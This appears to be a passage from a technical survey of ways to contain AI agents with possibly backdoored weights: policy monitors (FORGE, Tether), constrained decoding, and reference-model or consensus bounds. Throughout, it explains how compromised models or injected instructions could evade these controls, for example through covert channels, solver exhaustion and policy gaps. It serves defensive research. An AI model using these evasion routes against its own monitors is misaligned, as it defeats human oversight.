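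Neither obligation guarantees that the policy is right. Palumbo and colleagues had a language model translate an airline's written rules into Datalog five times. All five versions agreed with a model judge on every decision in the recorded runs used to build them, but one version blocked legitimate cancellations in all five trials of a new task. In the one construction run the researchers traced, every attempted cancellation had broken the rules, so a policy that refused all cancellations would have looked as good as a correct one.

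The example rule can fail when the weights are compromised, because it blocks secrets only if the agent has also read untrusted input. A backdoored model could email the internal file on a certain date without opening any outside document, and the rule would allow it. An owner who distrusts the weights would have to drop the taint condition and block every outgoing message that depends on a secret. Palumbo and colleagues also tested a policy that already works this way. It uses military-style clearances, and an agent may not read above its clearance or send to anyone below it.

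### Security and usefulness on AgentDojo

In a test with five trials, Palumbo and colleagues compared these policies with a prompt that told the agent not to leak data. With only the prompt, the agent sent top-secret merger plans to the attacker every time, because the planted text described the request as a mandatory compliance audit. With either policy, the agent leaked nothing and still completed the harmless task in every trial.

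Palumbo and colleagues compared two policies inside FORGE in a larger test on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do banking, travel and office tasks while attackers hide instructions in tool results. The agent ran on GPT-4o, and each configuration went through five rounds of 97 tasks without an attack and 949 runs with one. The information-flow policy, taken from an earlier system called FIDES, blocks any consequential action once the context contains untrusted content. It also blocks the disclosure of confidential data to a destination without clearance.

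Their own provenance policy checks the parts of an action individually: whether the user requested this kind of effect, and whether the recipient or target came from the user or another trusted source. In the results below, every agent also received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool results. The last column does not count an attack as successful if FORGE blocked all the calls it needed.

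| Protection | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attacks successful, benchmark's count | Attacks successful in effect |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reminder only | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% | 14.1% |
| Model picks permitted tools in advance | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% | 3.1% |
| FORGE, information-flow policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% | 0.3% |
| FORGE, provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% | 0.2% |

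The two FORGE policies provide about equal security, but under the information-flow policy the agent completes fewer than half of the tasks it otherwise would. One untrusted email is enough to block the consequential actions that follow. The provenance policy recovers most of that loss because it can still allow an action if the target came from the user. All the attacks that still succeeded in effect, 12 and 10 out of 4,745 runs under the two policies, had the agent recommend a particular hotel in its written reply. FORGE had nothing to block because a reply involves no tool call.

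Finer rules are also harder to get right. If a user asks the agent to delete the largest file, the request doesn't name the file, so the provenance policy finds the largest one in the listing and requires the agent's choice to match. But after deleting it, the agent could read the listing again and delete the next largest file. A search result containing only the attacker's file would also make that file the largest. The policy needed another rule to stop both. In three runs without the reminder, the agent booked the hotel an attacker wanted because no rule in the policy enforced the user's limits on price and rating.

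AgentDojo's attackers deceive an otherwise honest model, so these percentages do not predict what a compromised one would achieve. A model with harmful weights could search for gaps like the missing hotel rule. FORGE's guarantee still holds for such a model, but it covers only what the policy forbids.

### When the tool is a command line

FORGE works best when each tool does one known thing. Coding agents usually have a command line instead, and a single command can start a script that reads a hundred files and opens network connections. *Kairos* (2026) observes that a monitor tied to a declared list of tools does not cover scripts the agent writes and runs, and puts its monitor at the boundary of the agent's isolated environment, which every effect has to cross.

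Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, apply information-flow control at this lower level. They start from a dilemma: the text of a command doesn't reliably reveal what it will do, and running it to find out may do the damage. Their system therefore runs each command on a disposable copy:

1. Tether places a temporary layer over the file system. The command can read the real files, but its changes go into a scratch directory. A proxy holds each outgoing network request.
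2. It traces the command's system calls, which are the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, write to it or connect to another machine.
3. It translates the calls into a sequence of abstract actions. There are eleven kinds, including reading, copying, uploading and gaining administrator rights.
4. It checks each abstract action against the policy and updates the labels.
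5. If the policy allows them all, Tether commits the changes to the real file system. Otherwise it discards them.

Like the buffer in an edit automaton, the temporary layer lets a command continue as if its file changes had taken effect. This doesn't work for network requests, because the command may need a reply. Tether holds each request and decides whether to forward or drop it based on what the command has done so far.

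Tether keeps a label for each file, a taint for the agent's context and a record of the agent's privileges. If a command prints a file to the screen, the agent can read it, so the file's label joins the taint. If a command only copies a file, the label passes to the copy and the taint stays the same, because the contents never entered the agent's context. Tether over-approximates by assuming that data moved between two files whenever a program reads one and then writes the other.

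### The same upload, allowed and then denied

Suppose a company's server inventory is Sensitive and a status report is Public. The agent may read the inventory for local checks and may upload the report to an outside site. The policy's only rule for uploads is that the file must be Public. The agent then proposes three commands.

| Command | Abstract action | Report's label before | Decision | Report's label after |
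|---|---|---|---|---|
| Upload the report | upload | Public | allow | Public |
| Copy the inventory over the report | copy | Public | allow | Sensitive |
| Upload the report | upload | Sensitive | deny | Sensitive |

The two upload commands are identical, so a monitor that judged each command alone would have to treat them alike, either blocking a harmless upload or allowing a leak. Tether distinguishes them because the copy changed the report's label.

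A monitor could also search a log of past commands for a copy of the inventory. Sistla and colleagues show that this scales badly, because with m kinds of copying action, a chain of j copies can take mʲ forms. Covering all chains of up to k copies therefore takes m + m² + … + mᵏ patterns. For five kinds of copying and chains of up to four copies, that is 780 patterns, and an agent can evade them all by making a fifth copy. The monitor could instead block every file written after anyone has read the inventory, but this would also stop uploads of unrelated public files. With labels, one rule covers chains of any length, because each copy inherits the label of the file it was made from.

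### What the proofs in Lean cover

Sistla and colleagues wrote Tether's policy language in Lean 4, which is both a programming language and a proof checker. The definitions that the proofs are about therefore also run as the monitor. The team proved four general properties:

- Adding more permissive local rules cannot override a denial by an existing one.
- No local rule or exception can bypass a policy that the main policy requires.
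- The order in which someone writes the rules makes no difference.
- A denied action leaves the labels, taint and privileges unchanged.

They also proved seven properties of the 24-rule policy used in their experiments. For example, data labelled Secret never flows to a host outside the local network, and an agent that has seen sensitive or untrusted data cannot gain administrator rights. The proofs cover every starting state and every finite sequence of permitted abstract actions. Lean checks each step, so a language model's help in writing the proofs doesn't weaken the result.

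All of this concerns abstract actions, and there is no proof that Tether translates real system calls into the right ones. The guarantee therefore depends on something much like FORGE's obligation of faithful observation. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation with randomly generated scripts and with an agent whose task was to get past the monitor. The agent succeeded in 40% of its attempts against an early version and in none after three rounds of repairs. One of the gaps involved hard links, which give a file a second name.

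The repairs are encouraging, but the final test covered only ten tasks in a simple artificial environment and excluded actions that Tether does not model. The early failures show that a correct proof about the policy does not help if the monitor receives the wrong facts.

### Tether's results, and the runs they leave out

Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks for coding agents, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena. In a benign run the agent has an ordinary task, and in an adversarial run it also has a harmful one. The adversarial runs resemble a compromised model more closely than AgentDojo does, because the agent itself pursues the harmful goal.

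For comparison, the team ran Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a second language model reviews each proposed command. They tested it with its default instructions and again with Tether's policy added to them.

| Benchmark | Monitor | Attacks blocked | Benign runs blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | Tether | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| | Auto Mode, default | 173 of 199 | 77 of 218 (35.3%) |
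| | Auto Mode with the policy | 164 of 199 | 32 of 218 (14.7%) |
| LinuxArena | Tether | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |
| | Auto Mode, default | 142 of 145 | 78 of 1,372 (5.7%) |
| | Auto Mode with the policy | 143 of 145 | 23 of 1,372 (1.7%) |

Tether missed no attacks, but on LinuxArena the reviewing model with the policy missed only two and blocked fewer benign runs. The reviewing model did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts, whose effects the command line doesn't show. Of Tether's 74 false positives, 50 were edits to protected system files that the task had not called for and 7 were connections to undeclared hosts, and an owner might well want to know about both. The other 17 came from over-approximation. For instance, a search through the whole disk opens secret files, and Tether treats them as read by the agent.

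These figures overstate Tether's performance for two reasons. The team refined the policy by running it on traces from the benchmarks, so a policy written for unfamiliar work would probably block more benign runs or miss some attacks. The table also excludes runs with background actions or actions whose effects Tether could not model.

Many runs fell outside that scope. Sistla and colleagues report that 28.2% of runs on MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1% on LinuxArena required a judgement about content. For example, an agent that plants a malicious change in a source file it is allowed to edit breaks no rule about where data goes. A further 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively, involved background processes or databases, whose inner workings Tether does not yet track. These shares are for runs in general, not attacks alone, so the exact proportion of attacks left out is unclear. Tether can block background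 processes and databases, but many ordinary tasks need them, and the team reports no false-positive rate for that stricter policy.

### Why this approach suits compromised weights

In Tether's threat model, the adversary knows the whole policy and can issue any command. Its only limit is that it cannot alter or bypass the monitor. For the monitor's purposes, a model with compromised weights is exactly this adversary, and neither Tether's labels nor its proofs refer to the model's intentions.

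sasylabs, in *Securing AI agents*, makes the same claim for FORGE: its guarantee holds whether the agent is "well-behaved or adversarial". Both systems share this advantage with Ray's gate and extend it from payments and revoked access to the movement of data. Some related designs lack it because they rely on an honest planner to choose the agent's steps.

If the weights are compromised, the owner has to assign labels differently. Tether starts the agent's context at the lowest label, which assumes that an agent that has read nothing holds no secret data. But a model fine-tuned on customer records may be able to reproduce them without a read that would raise the taint. The owner would have to either keep such data out of training or start the context at the label of the most sensitive training data, which would block most outgoing messages from the first step.

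## The case for restricting which tokens may come next

FORGE and Tether act only after the model has written a complete tool call or command. A shield can also act while the model is still writing, by blocking any token that would lead to a forbidden call. This method is called constrained decoding, and developers already use it widely to make models produce data that other software can read. Its appeal for security is that it prevents the model from writing a forbidden call, which removes the need to detect one afterward.

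### Masks and completable texts

At each step, a token mask sets the probability of each forbidden token to zero and rescales the remaining probabilities to add up to one. The software then picks a token as usual.

*ChopChop* (Nagy, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) defines precisely which tokens to forbid. Let Φ be a rule about finished texts. An unfinished text ω is completable if some continuation ω′ makes the whole text ωω′ satisfy Φ. The shield forbids every token that would make the text impossible to complete in this sense, and lets the model stop only when the text satisfies Φ. A text that is not completable resembles a bad prefix, because it breaks the rule however the model continues.

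A program called a checker decides whether a text is completable. The checker is sound if every text it accepts is completable, and complete if it accepts every completable text. Nagy and colleagues define the same two properties for the decoding procedure as a whole:

- It is sound if every text it returns satisfies Φ.
- It is complete if it can return every text that satisfies Φ with a probability above zero.

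Their procedure also tests the finished text against Φ before returning it. If this test is sound, the procedure never returns a forbidden text, even when the checker is unsound. An unsound checker can still lead the model into a dead end, where no continuation works.

Completeness in a checker is much like transparency in a monitor. With a complete checker and the usual random sampling methods, masking never makes any compliant text less likely. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (2026) reports that an incomplete checker can reduce the functional correctness of generated code by up to 97%.

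### An email with three approved recipients

Suppose the owner of the office assistant allows it to write emails only in this form:

```
call      ::= 'send_email(to="' recipient '", body="' text '")'
recipient ::= 'anna@office.example' | 'andrew@office.example' | 'ben@office.example'
text      ::= any characters except a quotation mark
```

A backdoor now makes the model try to write to an outsider called Eve. The table shows some possible next tokens at two steps, with invented probabilities. A 1 in the mask column means the token is allowed.

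| Text so far | Next token | Model's probability | Mask | Probability after masking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `send_email(to="` | `eve` | 0.90 | 0 | 0 |
| | `an` | 0.06 | 1 | 0.60 |
| | `ben` | 0.04 | 1 | 0.40 |
| `send_email(to="an` | `onymous` | 0.70 | 0 | 0 |
| | `na` | 0.24 | 1 | 0.80 |
| | `drew` | 0.06 | 1 | 0.20 |

At the first step, the mask allows `an` because two approved addresses begin with it, even though forbidden addresses do too. At the next step, it blocks `onymous` because no approved address begins with `anonymous`. The model cannot stop at either step because the call is unfinished. It also cannot add a BCC field, since the grammar has none.

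*Only What You've Signed up For* (Cardei, Pinto and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that restricts which tokens may come next in tool names, recipients and other sensitive fields. In tests where attackers hid instructions in the results of tool calls, no attack succeeded when the system had the correct policy for each task. The system did not restrict text outside the sensitive fields.

### Automata and grammars

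A finite automaton can check the simplest rules, such as a list of addresses or a date format, by reading the text one character at a time. Software can work out in advance which tokens each state allows, so applying the mask takes little more than a lookup. But a finite automaton cannot check that brackets match when they may be nested to any depth, because counting them would take an unlimited number of states.

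Even these rules are harder to enforce on diffusion language models, which fill in many positions of a text at once. In *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata*, Dang and Ermon (2026) give the example of a two-character number. Both "1." and ".1" are valid, so a full stop is allowed in either position, but choosing it in both gives "..", which is not a number. Their method considers all positions together. It raised one model's accuracy on a test of function calls from 63.9% to 71.5% and added less than 5% to the running time.

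A context-free grammar can describe nesting, because its checker keeps a stack of the brackets still open. Such grammars cover the syntax of most data formats and programming languages. Computing a mask typically takes longer with a larger vocabulary, but *Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (2026) describes a method up to 700 times faster than earlier ones on complex grammars. With this method, a model generates text almost as fast as it would without a mask.

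The main difficulty is that tokens do not match the units of the grammar. A token may contain only part of an address, or the end of one and the quotation mark after it, so the checker has to check every character. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (Li, Rahili and Zhao, 2025) points out that an earlier method can accept a long token that begins correctly and ends incorrectly. In the email example, this error could let the token `example.net` turn Ben's approved address into `ben@office.example.net`, which may belong to someone else.

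Errors in constrained-decoding tools are common enough to matter. *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025) showed that some optimised tools let forbidden texts through and others blocked permitted ones, and it proposed a simpler design called GreatGramma. In *Machine-Checked Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, Bhat, Dandu and colleagues (2026) tried to prove that design correct in Lean and found a bug that could let the model stop in the middle of a unit.

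The corrected version allows exactly the tokens that can still lead to a valid text, provided certain assumptions hold. One assumption is that whitespace can go between any two units without changing the meaning. This may not hold for Python, where indentation matters.

### Types and program behaviour

A grammar controls only the form of a text. When Nagy and colleagues constrained a model with a grammar for a small programming language, it wrote an English sentence beginning "Here is an equivalent refactored version", which the grammar accepted as a series of function calls. A rule that excludes such a sentence must also cover meaning, such as which variables exist and what type each has.

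Such rules are harder to enforce with a mask than with a check on the finished program. The check covers one program, but computing the mask requires determining whether any of infinitely many continuations would pass. Nagy and colleagues note that this can be undecidable even when checking a finished program is decidable.

For a subset of TypeScript, they therefore use a checker that is complete but not sound. With it, CodeLlama-13B wrote programs that compiled in 319 of 360 runs, compared with 259 without constraints. Checking added between 107 and 173 milliseconds per token to the 81 the model normally needs.

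Li and colleagues avoided some of these difficulties by designing a restricted language. Their system writes scripts for new abilities in a video game while someone is playing, so no programmer can fix a mistake. The scripts are in sLua, a strictly typed variant of the language Lua. The system repeats three steps:

1. The parser works out a pattern for the next piece of the script from the variables that exist at that point and their types. If the script needs a number, the pattern excludes names that stand for text.
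2. The model writes a piece that matches the pattern.
3. The parser reads the piece and updates its list of variables.

sLua has no recursion and no data structures that grow, and a "while" loop stops after 100 rounds. The functions that the game offers to scripts never fail when their arguments have the right types. From this, Li and colleagues prove that every script the system completes will terminate and run without errors.

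In the main experiment, each method generated sets of four abilities and up to four related effects, with ten runs for each of eight themes. The constrained model, Qwen2.5-32B-Coder, had the highest success rate. It failed only when it had not finished after 1,500 tokens, whereas unconstrained models typically failed by inventing variables or making syntax errors.

The guarantee did not produce the best scripts, though. When the methods could retry after an error, unconstrained Claude 3.5 Sonnet produced 38 sets that scored 90 or more out of 100, against 33 for the constrained model. Claude 3.5 Sonnet also did the scoring, which may have biased the results in its favour. The constrained model generated 7.64 tokens a second, compared with 18.89 without constraints.

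A mask can trap a model. In one failure, the model tried to begin a comment with two slashes, although sLua has no comments. The mask allowed the first slash as a division sign but blocked the second, and the model then wrote repetitive arithmetic until it reached the limit.

### When the solver gives no verdict

The most expressive rules so far are in *AGDecode* (Maghera, Arya and colleagues, 2026). It uses attribute grammars, which attach values to each part of a program, such as its type, and give equations for computing them. *AGDecode* treats the parts that the model has not yet written as unknowns, translates the equations into logical formulas, and uses a separate program, called a solver, to check whether any way of filling in the unknowns would satisfy the rule.

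AGDecode stops a model from writing C programs that divide by zero, use a variable before giving it a value, or follow an invalid pointer. In one example, it lets the model write code that looks up an item in a list because the program has already checked that the list exists, but blocks the lookup if that check is removed.

Maghera and colleagues prove that the method is sound and complete if the solver always reaches a correct verdict. Real solvers sometimes run out of time. When that happens, AGDecode's conservative mode rejects the token, which is safe but may block a valid program. Its speculative mode accepts the token and relies on a later query, which covers the whole text so far, to find any error.

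The main experiment used speculative mode and tested CodeLlama-13B on 77 programming tasks, at three settings for how randomly the model picks tokens. The solver had five seconds per query. Over 11,804 queries, it rejected the text in 43% of cases, approved it in 34% and reached no verdict in 23%. At each setting, the median rejection took one or two milliseconds, while the median approval took between 1.1 and 2 seconds. Most timeouts happened in the middle of an expression, and the query often became easy once the statement was complete.

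Maghera and colleagues illustrate the effect with examples but do not report the overall share of programs that were safe. Their prototype also could not replace earlier tokens when a later query failed. The experiment is therefore better evidence of the method's overhead than of how many errors it prevents.

The choice of mode matters a great deal when the weights are compromised, because a malicious model could write expressions that exhaust the solver. In speculative mode, the shield would have to get a definite verdict on the finished program before anyone runs it, and discard the program if it can't get one. In conservative mode, the model could waste time but could not get a violation through.

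### What the mask guarantees when the weights are compromised

A mask works the same way whatever probabilities the model produces, and the proof by Bhat and colleagues holds for any weights. If the mask is correct, a backdoored assistant cannot put Eve's address in the recipient field, even if it gives that address a probability of 99.9%.

But the model still chooses among the permitted texts. The body of the email is free text, so the assistant could send Ben a colleague's medical note. *Decode-Time Grammars* (2026) measures the remaining freedom by summing log₂ of the number of allowed tokens at each step. A step with two allowed tokens adds 1 bit, and a step in free text with a vocabulary of 131,072 tokens adds at most 17 bits. A compromised model could use this freedom to pass on information. *Grammar-as-a-Drafter* (2026) notes that even when the text is fixed, the model may be able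 to spell it with different token sequences.

The model can also keep generating indefinitely, because a grammar that allows a body of any length does not force it to end, so the shield needs its own limits on length and time. Speed measured on honest models is a poor guide to speed on malicious ones. Li and colleagues save time by testing the model's top-ranked token first and moving to another only if it fails. This works well when most first choices are valid, as they were for 96.4% of the tokens in the TypeScript tests by Nagy and colleagues. But a malicious model could rank thousands of forbidden tokens above the first permitted one.

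### Masking the tokens or checking the finished call

For tool calls, a check on the finished call can prevent anything a token mask could, because a monitor can still block the call before it runs. For example, it can compare an email's recipient with the approved list before the email is sent. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) checks finished calls against a policy written in Lean. In tests with five Qwen models, agents without the check carried out at least 33 forbidden calls, and agents with it carried out none. When the system told agents which rule they had broken, their success at the tasks did not change significantly.

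A mask can even make matters worse. In the email example, the model was about to address the message to Eve, and the mask redirected it to a colleague. If the body contains confidential data, the colleague may now receive information they should not see, whereas a monitor would have blocked the email. *Repair, Not Improvement* (2026) stresses that a model choosing tools must also be able to call no tool. For security, the grammar should also let the model abandon a call it has already begun.

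Unlike a monitor, a mask needs access to the model's probabilities before the software picks a token. Someone who runs a downloaded model has this access, but a customer of a hosted service depends on the provider to apply the mask. The mask must also handle tokenisation correctly, while a monitor can ignore tokens and read the finished call.

A mask can also become outdated if the rules change. *From Grammar Deltas to Token Masks* (2026) studies grammars that change after the model has begun to write. If the owner removes Ben from the list while the model is writing, a mask built from the old list could still allow his address, but a monitor would use the current list.

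A mask mainly helps by reducing the number of attempts the model wastes on malformed or forbidden calls. It can also help when a user reads the reply as the model writes it, because there is no finished call to check first. A shield could hold back the reply until it is complete, but the user would have to wait. For tool calls, an owner can use a mask and keep a monitor behind it. The monitor then provides the guarantee, so if the mask lets a forbidden recipient through, the monitor blocks the call.

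## The case for bounding outputs by a trusted reference model

A token mask forbids some texts and leaves the model free to choose among the rest. It can't help when the forbidden texts share no form that a grammar could describe. Another kind of shield limits the model's freedom by comparing it with a reference model that the owner trusts. This shield rejects any output to which the untrusted model gives a far higher probability than the reference model does.

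A backdoor that makes a model write one particular message has to give that message a high probability, while a clean reference model gives it a tiny one. The shield can detect this gap even if the message looks innocent to every reader.

### A definition from copyright law

The method comes from research on copyright. Vyas, Kakade and Barak (2023), in *On Provable Copyright Protection for Generative Models*, wanted to limit how often a model reproduces a protected work from its training data. They compare the model p with a "safe" model that trained without access to that work. The model p is k-near access-free if, for every protected work, every prompt x and every output y,

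p(y | x) ≤ 2^k · safe(y | x).

Each extra bit of k doubles the permitted ratio. Summing the inequality over the outputs in a set E gives the same bound for the set: p(E | x) ≤ 2^k · safe(E | x). If safe was trained without a particular novel, it is very unlikely to reproduce a page of it by accident, so when k is small, p is also very unlikely to do so.

To build such a model, Vyas and colleagues split the training data in half and train a model on each half. The combined model gives each output the smaller of the two models' probabilities, rescaled so that the probabilities of all outputs add up to one. Suppose each model outputs a different memorised text half the time and the two otherwise behave alike. Each memorised text then has zero probability under the other model, so the combined model never produces it.

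The second algorithm, CP-k, works with any model p. It draws outputs from p and accepts the first one that p makes at most 2^k times as likely as each safe model does. In a test on small images, repeated copies of two pictures stood in for protected works and made up about 2% of the training data. CP-k rejected 3.5% of the outputs, and none of 2,000 accepted images was a copy.

Drawing again without limit is dangerous if p is compromised. The model could give a forbidden text a probability just low enough to pass and assign the rest of its probability to texts that fail. The shield would then reject every draw until the forbidden text came up. The bound proved by Vyas and colleagues accounts for this by adding log₂(1/ν) to k, where ν is the share of draws that pass, but a malicious model can make ν as small as the attack requires.

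Cohen (2026), in *Blameless Users in a Clean Room*, proves that rescaling can do similar damage. With some training algorithms, a prompt that describes only the ideas in a training text makes the combined model reproduce that text word for word. One half-model always writes the text and the other almost never does. Because the text is the only output that both can produce, rescaling raises its probability to 100%.

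### VALID, step by step

Emde, Paren and colleagues (2025), in *Shh, Don't Say That! Domain Certification in LLMs*, adapted CP-k to keep chatbots on their subject, such as health advice. Their method, VALID, limits the number of draws. It uses an untrusted model L, a reference model G trained only on texts about the subject, a limit of k bits per token and a maximum of T attempts:

1. Draw a complete reply y from L for the prompt x, and count its tokens, N.
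2. Compute L(y | x) and G(y). G does not receive the prompt, so an attacker cannot use the prompt to manipulate it.
3. If log₂(L(y | x) / G(y)) ≤ kN, return y.
4. Otherwise discard y and start again. After T failures, return no reply.

The limit grows with N because the ratio grows with length even for good replies. If L gives each token a probability of 0.1 and G gives it 0.05, the ratio doubles with every token, so a fixed limit would reject every long reply.

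Let M be the whole system. Emde and colleagues prove that, for every prompt x and every reply y,

M(y | x) ≤ 2^(kN) · T · G(y).

If y fails the test, M never returns it, so the bound holds trivially. If y passes, then L(y | x) ≤ 2^(kN) · G(y). M can return y in a given round only if L draws it, which happens with probability L(y | x), and so at most 2^(kN) · G(y). Since there are at most T rounds, the total probability that M returns y is at most T · 2^(kN) · G(y).

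### Why the bound survives compromised weights

The proof assumes nothing about L, so the bound holds even if the weights contain a backdoor planted by someone who knows G, k and T. If L gives a forbidden reply a high probability, the reply fails the test, and if L gives it a low probability, L rarely draws it. The bound holds for every prompt, including those that contain a trigger phrase.

The test must use the probability with which the software actually drew y. Software that always picks the most likely token produces its text with probability 1, so the test must use 1 instead of the product of the model's token probabilities. The random numbers must also be outside the attacker's control.

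Both models must also score the same sequence of tokens. If G scored only the finished text, L could spread a forbidden message's probability over many token sequences that spell the same text, each unlikely enough to pass. The owner therefore has to trust the code that runs the models, and also has to trust G, because the bound on a reply is low only if G gives that reply a low probability.

### One forbidden string, and a large set of them

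Suppose k is 2 bits per token, a reply has 20 tokens and T is 4. The multiplier in the bound is then 2⁴⁰ · 4 = 2⁴². If G gives each token of a forbidden reply a probability of 2⁻⁷, a little under 1%, it gives the whole reply a probability of 2⁻¹⁴⁰. The compromised system therefore returns that reply with a probability of at most 2⁻⁹⁸, or about 3 in 10³⁰. The bound is even lower for longer replies of this kind, because each extra token multiplies it by 2² · 2⁻⁷ = 2⁻⁵.

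But an attacker seldom needs one exact wording. For a set F of forbidden 20-token replies, the bound is 2⁴² · G(F), which is useful only if G(F) is much less than 2⁻⁴², about one in four trillion. A reference model that wrote something forbidden once in a billion replies would be excellent by ordinary standards, but the bound would exceed 1 and guarantee nothing. The owner also could not practically confirm a rate below one in four trillion by sampling from G.

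Forbidden sets can easily be this large. If an attacker has about 30 usable choices for each of the 20 tokens, there are about 2⁹⁸ wordings, and individual bounds of 2⁻⁹⁸ add up to about 1. Longer replies weaken the guarantee further. At 200 tokens the multiplier is 2⁴⁰², while G(F) may not fall at all, since a longer email has more places to mention a diagnosis. VALID can therefore give a strong guarantee against one long text, such as a memorised document, but usually not against a category as broad as "any reply that reveals personal data".

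*Anchored Decoding* (2026) divides a fixed budget for the whole output among the tokens, so the total does not grow with length. However, the budget limits the average log-ratio (the Kullback–Leibler divergence) and not its maximum, which lets a malicious model raise the probability of a chosen token further. With an average of 2 bits at each step, the model could raise that probability from under 1% to about 42%. It could then write the forbidden 20-token string about once in 30 million replies. If 2 bits per token were the maximum, the probability of writing the string in a single attempt would be at most 2⁻¹⁰⁰, about one in 10³⁰.

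Short outputs with few alternatives suit the method better. For the calendar rule, a reference model could receive the list of free slots without the reasons the others are busy. If eight slots are free and the reference model gives each a probability of 1/8, then with one attempt and a total limit of 1 bit, no slot's probability can exceed 1/4, whatever the private entries contain. This only approximates the rule, since a refusal to answer can also reveal something. Another drawback is that the shield would reject an honest assistant that always proposes the earliest slot, because that assistant gives one slot a probability of 1.

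### Tests on three subjects

Emde and colleagues trained each reference model from scratch and kept it far smaller than the model it was meant to check.

| Subject | Untrusted model | Weights in the reference model | Off-topic texts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shakespeare's plays | Gemma-2-2b | 33.7 million | Film reviews, an old Bible and other texts |
| Computer science news | Gemma-2-2b | 109.3 million | The same, plus other news topics |
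| Medical questions | Llama-3-8B | 184 million | Questions on other subjects |

With k set so that VALID rejected 10% of the on-topic texts, the bound was below 10⁻¹⁰ for 95% of the off-topic texts in all three subjects. In the medical test, the median bound was about 24 orders of magnitude below the untrusted model's probability of producing the same text after an ordinary prompt.

Tighter guarantees require rejecting more good answers. With a single attempt, VALID had to reject 15% of the on-topic texts to bring the bound below 10⁻⁵ for every off-topic text in the medical test set. On PubMedQA, a benchmark of medical questions, the score fell from 73.4% without a guarantee to 66.7% with a bound of 10⁻⁵ and 47.7% with a bound of 10⁻¹⁰.

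These bounds apply to each text separately. Emde and colleagues suggest that a service that handles ten requests a second and can tolerate one off-topic reply a year needs a bound of about 10⁻⁹. That is right if only one possible reply is forbidden, but if a million are, the bounds add up to one in a thousand per request, which would allow a forbidden reply every 100 seconds.

In the medical test, Emde and colleagues also trained the reference model further on the untrusted model's answers. This would be a mistake with compromised weights, because the answers could train the reference model to give harmful texts a higher probability.

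Keeping a model on its subject does not make its answers right. "Once a year" is a sensible answer to how often to file a tax return but not to how often to shower, yet a reference model that never receives the question gives it the same score in both cases. Emde and colleagues add that such a small model probably cannot distinguish similar sentences with opposite meanings. A backdoored medical assistant could therefore recommend the wrong dose in ordinary medical language and still pass the reference model's check.

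### Agreement among several models

An owner may have no single model to trust, but may believe that most of a group are safe without knowing which. Kalai, Kalai and Zamir (2025), in *Consensus Sampling for Safer Generative AI*, designed an algorithm for this case. It uses n models, of which at least s are safe, and allows up to R rounds:

1. Pick one of the models at random and draw an output y from it.
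2. Compute the probability that each of the n models gives y.
3. Let a be the average of the s smallest of these probabilities and b the average of all n. Return y with probability a/b.
4. Otherwise start another round. After R failures, abstain, which means returning nothing.

The table shows two outputs with invented probabilities for three models, where s is 2 and the third model has a backdoor.

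| Output | Model 1 | Model 2 | Model 3 | a | b | Chance of acceptance |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary reply | 0.02 | 0.03 | 0.04 | 0.025 | 0.03 | 83% |
| Backdoor's message | 0.000001 | 0.000003 | 0.9 | 0.000002 | 0.3 | 0.0007% |

In one round, the algorithm draws an output y with probability b and accepts it with probability a/b, so it returns y with probability a. Here a is the average of the s smallest probabilities that the models assign to y, so it cannot exceed the average over any s models, including the s safest. Summing over any set of unsafe outputs and over R rounds shows that the risk of returning an unsafe output is at most R times the average risk of the s safest models.

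With five rounds, this bound limits the risk to five times that of the safe models, regardless of the reply's length or the forbidden set's size. The bound has no factor of 2^(kN), and nobody has to define the forbidden set in advance. An attacker would have to plant the same backdoor in more than n − s models to get past the algorithm reliably.

The drawback is abstention, which has probability (1 − Z)^R over R rounds. Z is the sum of a over all possible outputs and depends on how much the models overlap. The overlap of two models is the sum, over all outputs, of the smaller of their two probabilities. If two of three models are safe and their overlap is 0.2, Z is at least 0.1. Getting the abstention rate below 1% could then take 44 rounds, which would also raise the limit on risk to 44 times that of the safe models.

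Two honest models may prefer different words or punctuation, and Kalai and colleagues warn that their overlap may shrink exponentially as texts get longer. They expect more overlap for yes-or-no decisions and tightly specified answers such as chemical formulas. Overlap might also be high for a tool call with a few fixed fields, but probably not for a free-form email.

The algorithm also limits how much information the compromised models can pass on. It is equivalent to having the safe models draw R candidate replies and letting the compromised models influence only which candidate is returned, if any. There are R + 1 possible outcomes, so the compromised models can leak at most log₂(R + 1) bits per prompt, or about 2.3 bits for R = 4. Whether that is enough to do harm depends on what the bits mean to the recipient.

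The total also grows with every prompt. Cohen proves that near access-freeness has the corresponding weakness. However small k is, some models that satisfy the definition let a user recover all the training data with enough prompts.

Kalai and colleagues tested consensus sampling on three image sources. Two generated ordinary pictures with the model Janus-Pro-7B, and the third used the same model but hid a fictitious credit card number in each picture. Their decoder recovered the number from all 150 of the third source's pictures. Choosing a source at random would return such a picture a third of the time. Consensus sampling returned none in 30 trials at any setting, and its abstention rate fell from 37% with one round to zero with four.

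Kalai and colleagues acknowledge that the test was easy. The third source gave its own picture a probability of 1, which made it as conspicuous as possible. The two ordinary sources were the same model, so they overlapped completely, unlike models from different companies.

### A sampler that always answers

*Towards Provably Secure Generative AI* (2025) argues that consensus sampling abstains too often to be practical, and that compromised models can make it abstain more by giving good replies very low probabilities. The paper proposes Reliable Consensus Sampling, which works in the same way until all R rounds have failed. It then shortlists up to s rejected replies with the highest chances of acceptance, adds up the n − s largest probabilities that the models gave each one, and returns the reply with the largest sum.

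According to the paper, the risk is still at most n times the average risk of the safe models, plus a negligible amount, where n is the number of models. The proof treats (1 − Z)^R, the probability that all R rounds fail, as negligible because R is large, but it also requires R to be no larger than n. If that probability were negligible, ordinary consensus sampling would almost never abstain and would need no remedy. In the paper's experiments, it abstained in about three quarters of the runs.

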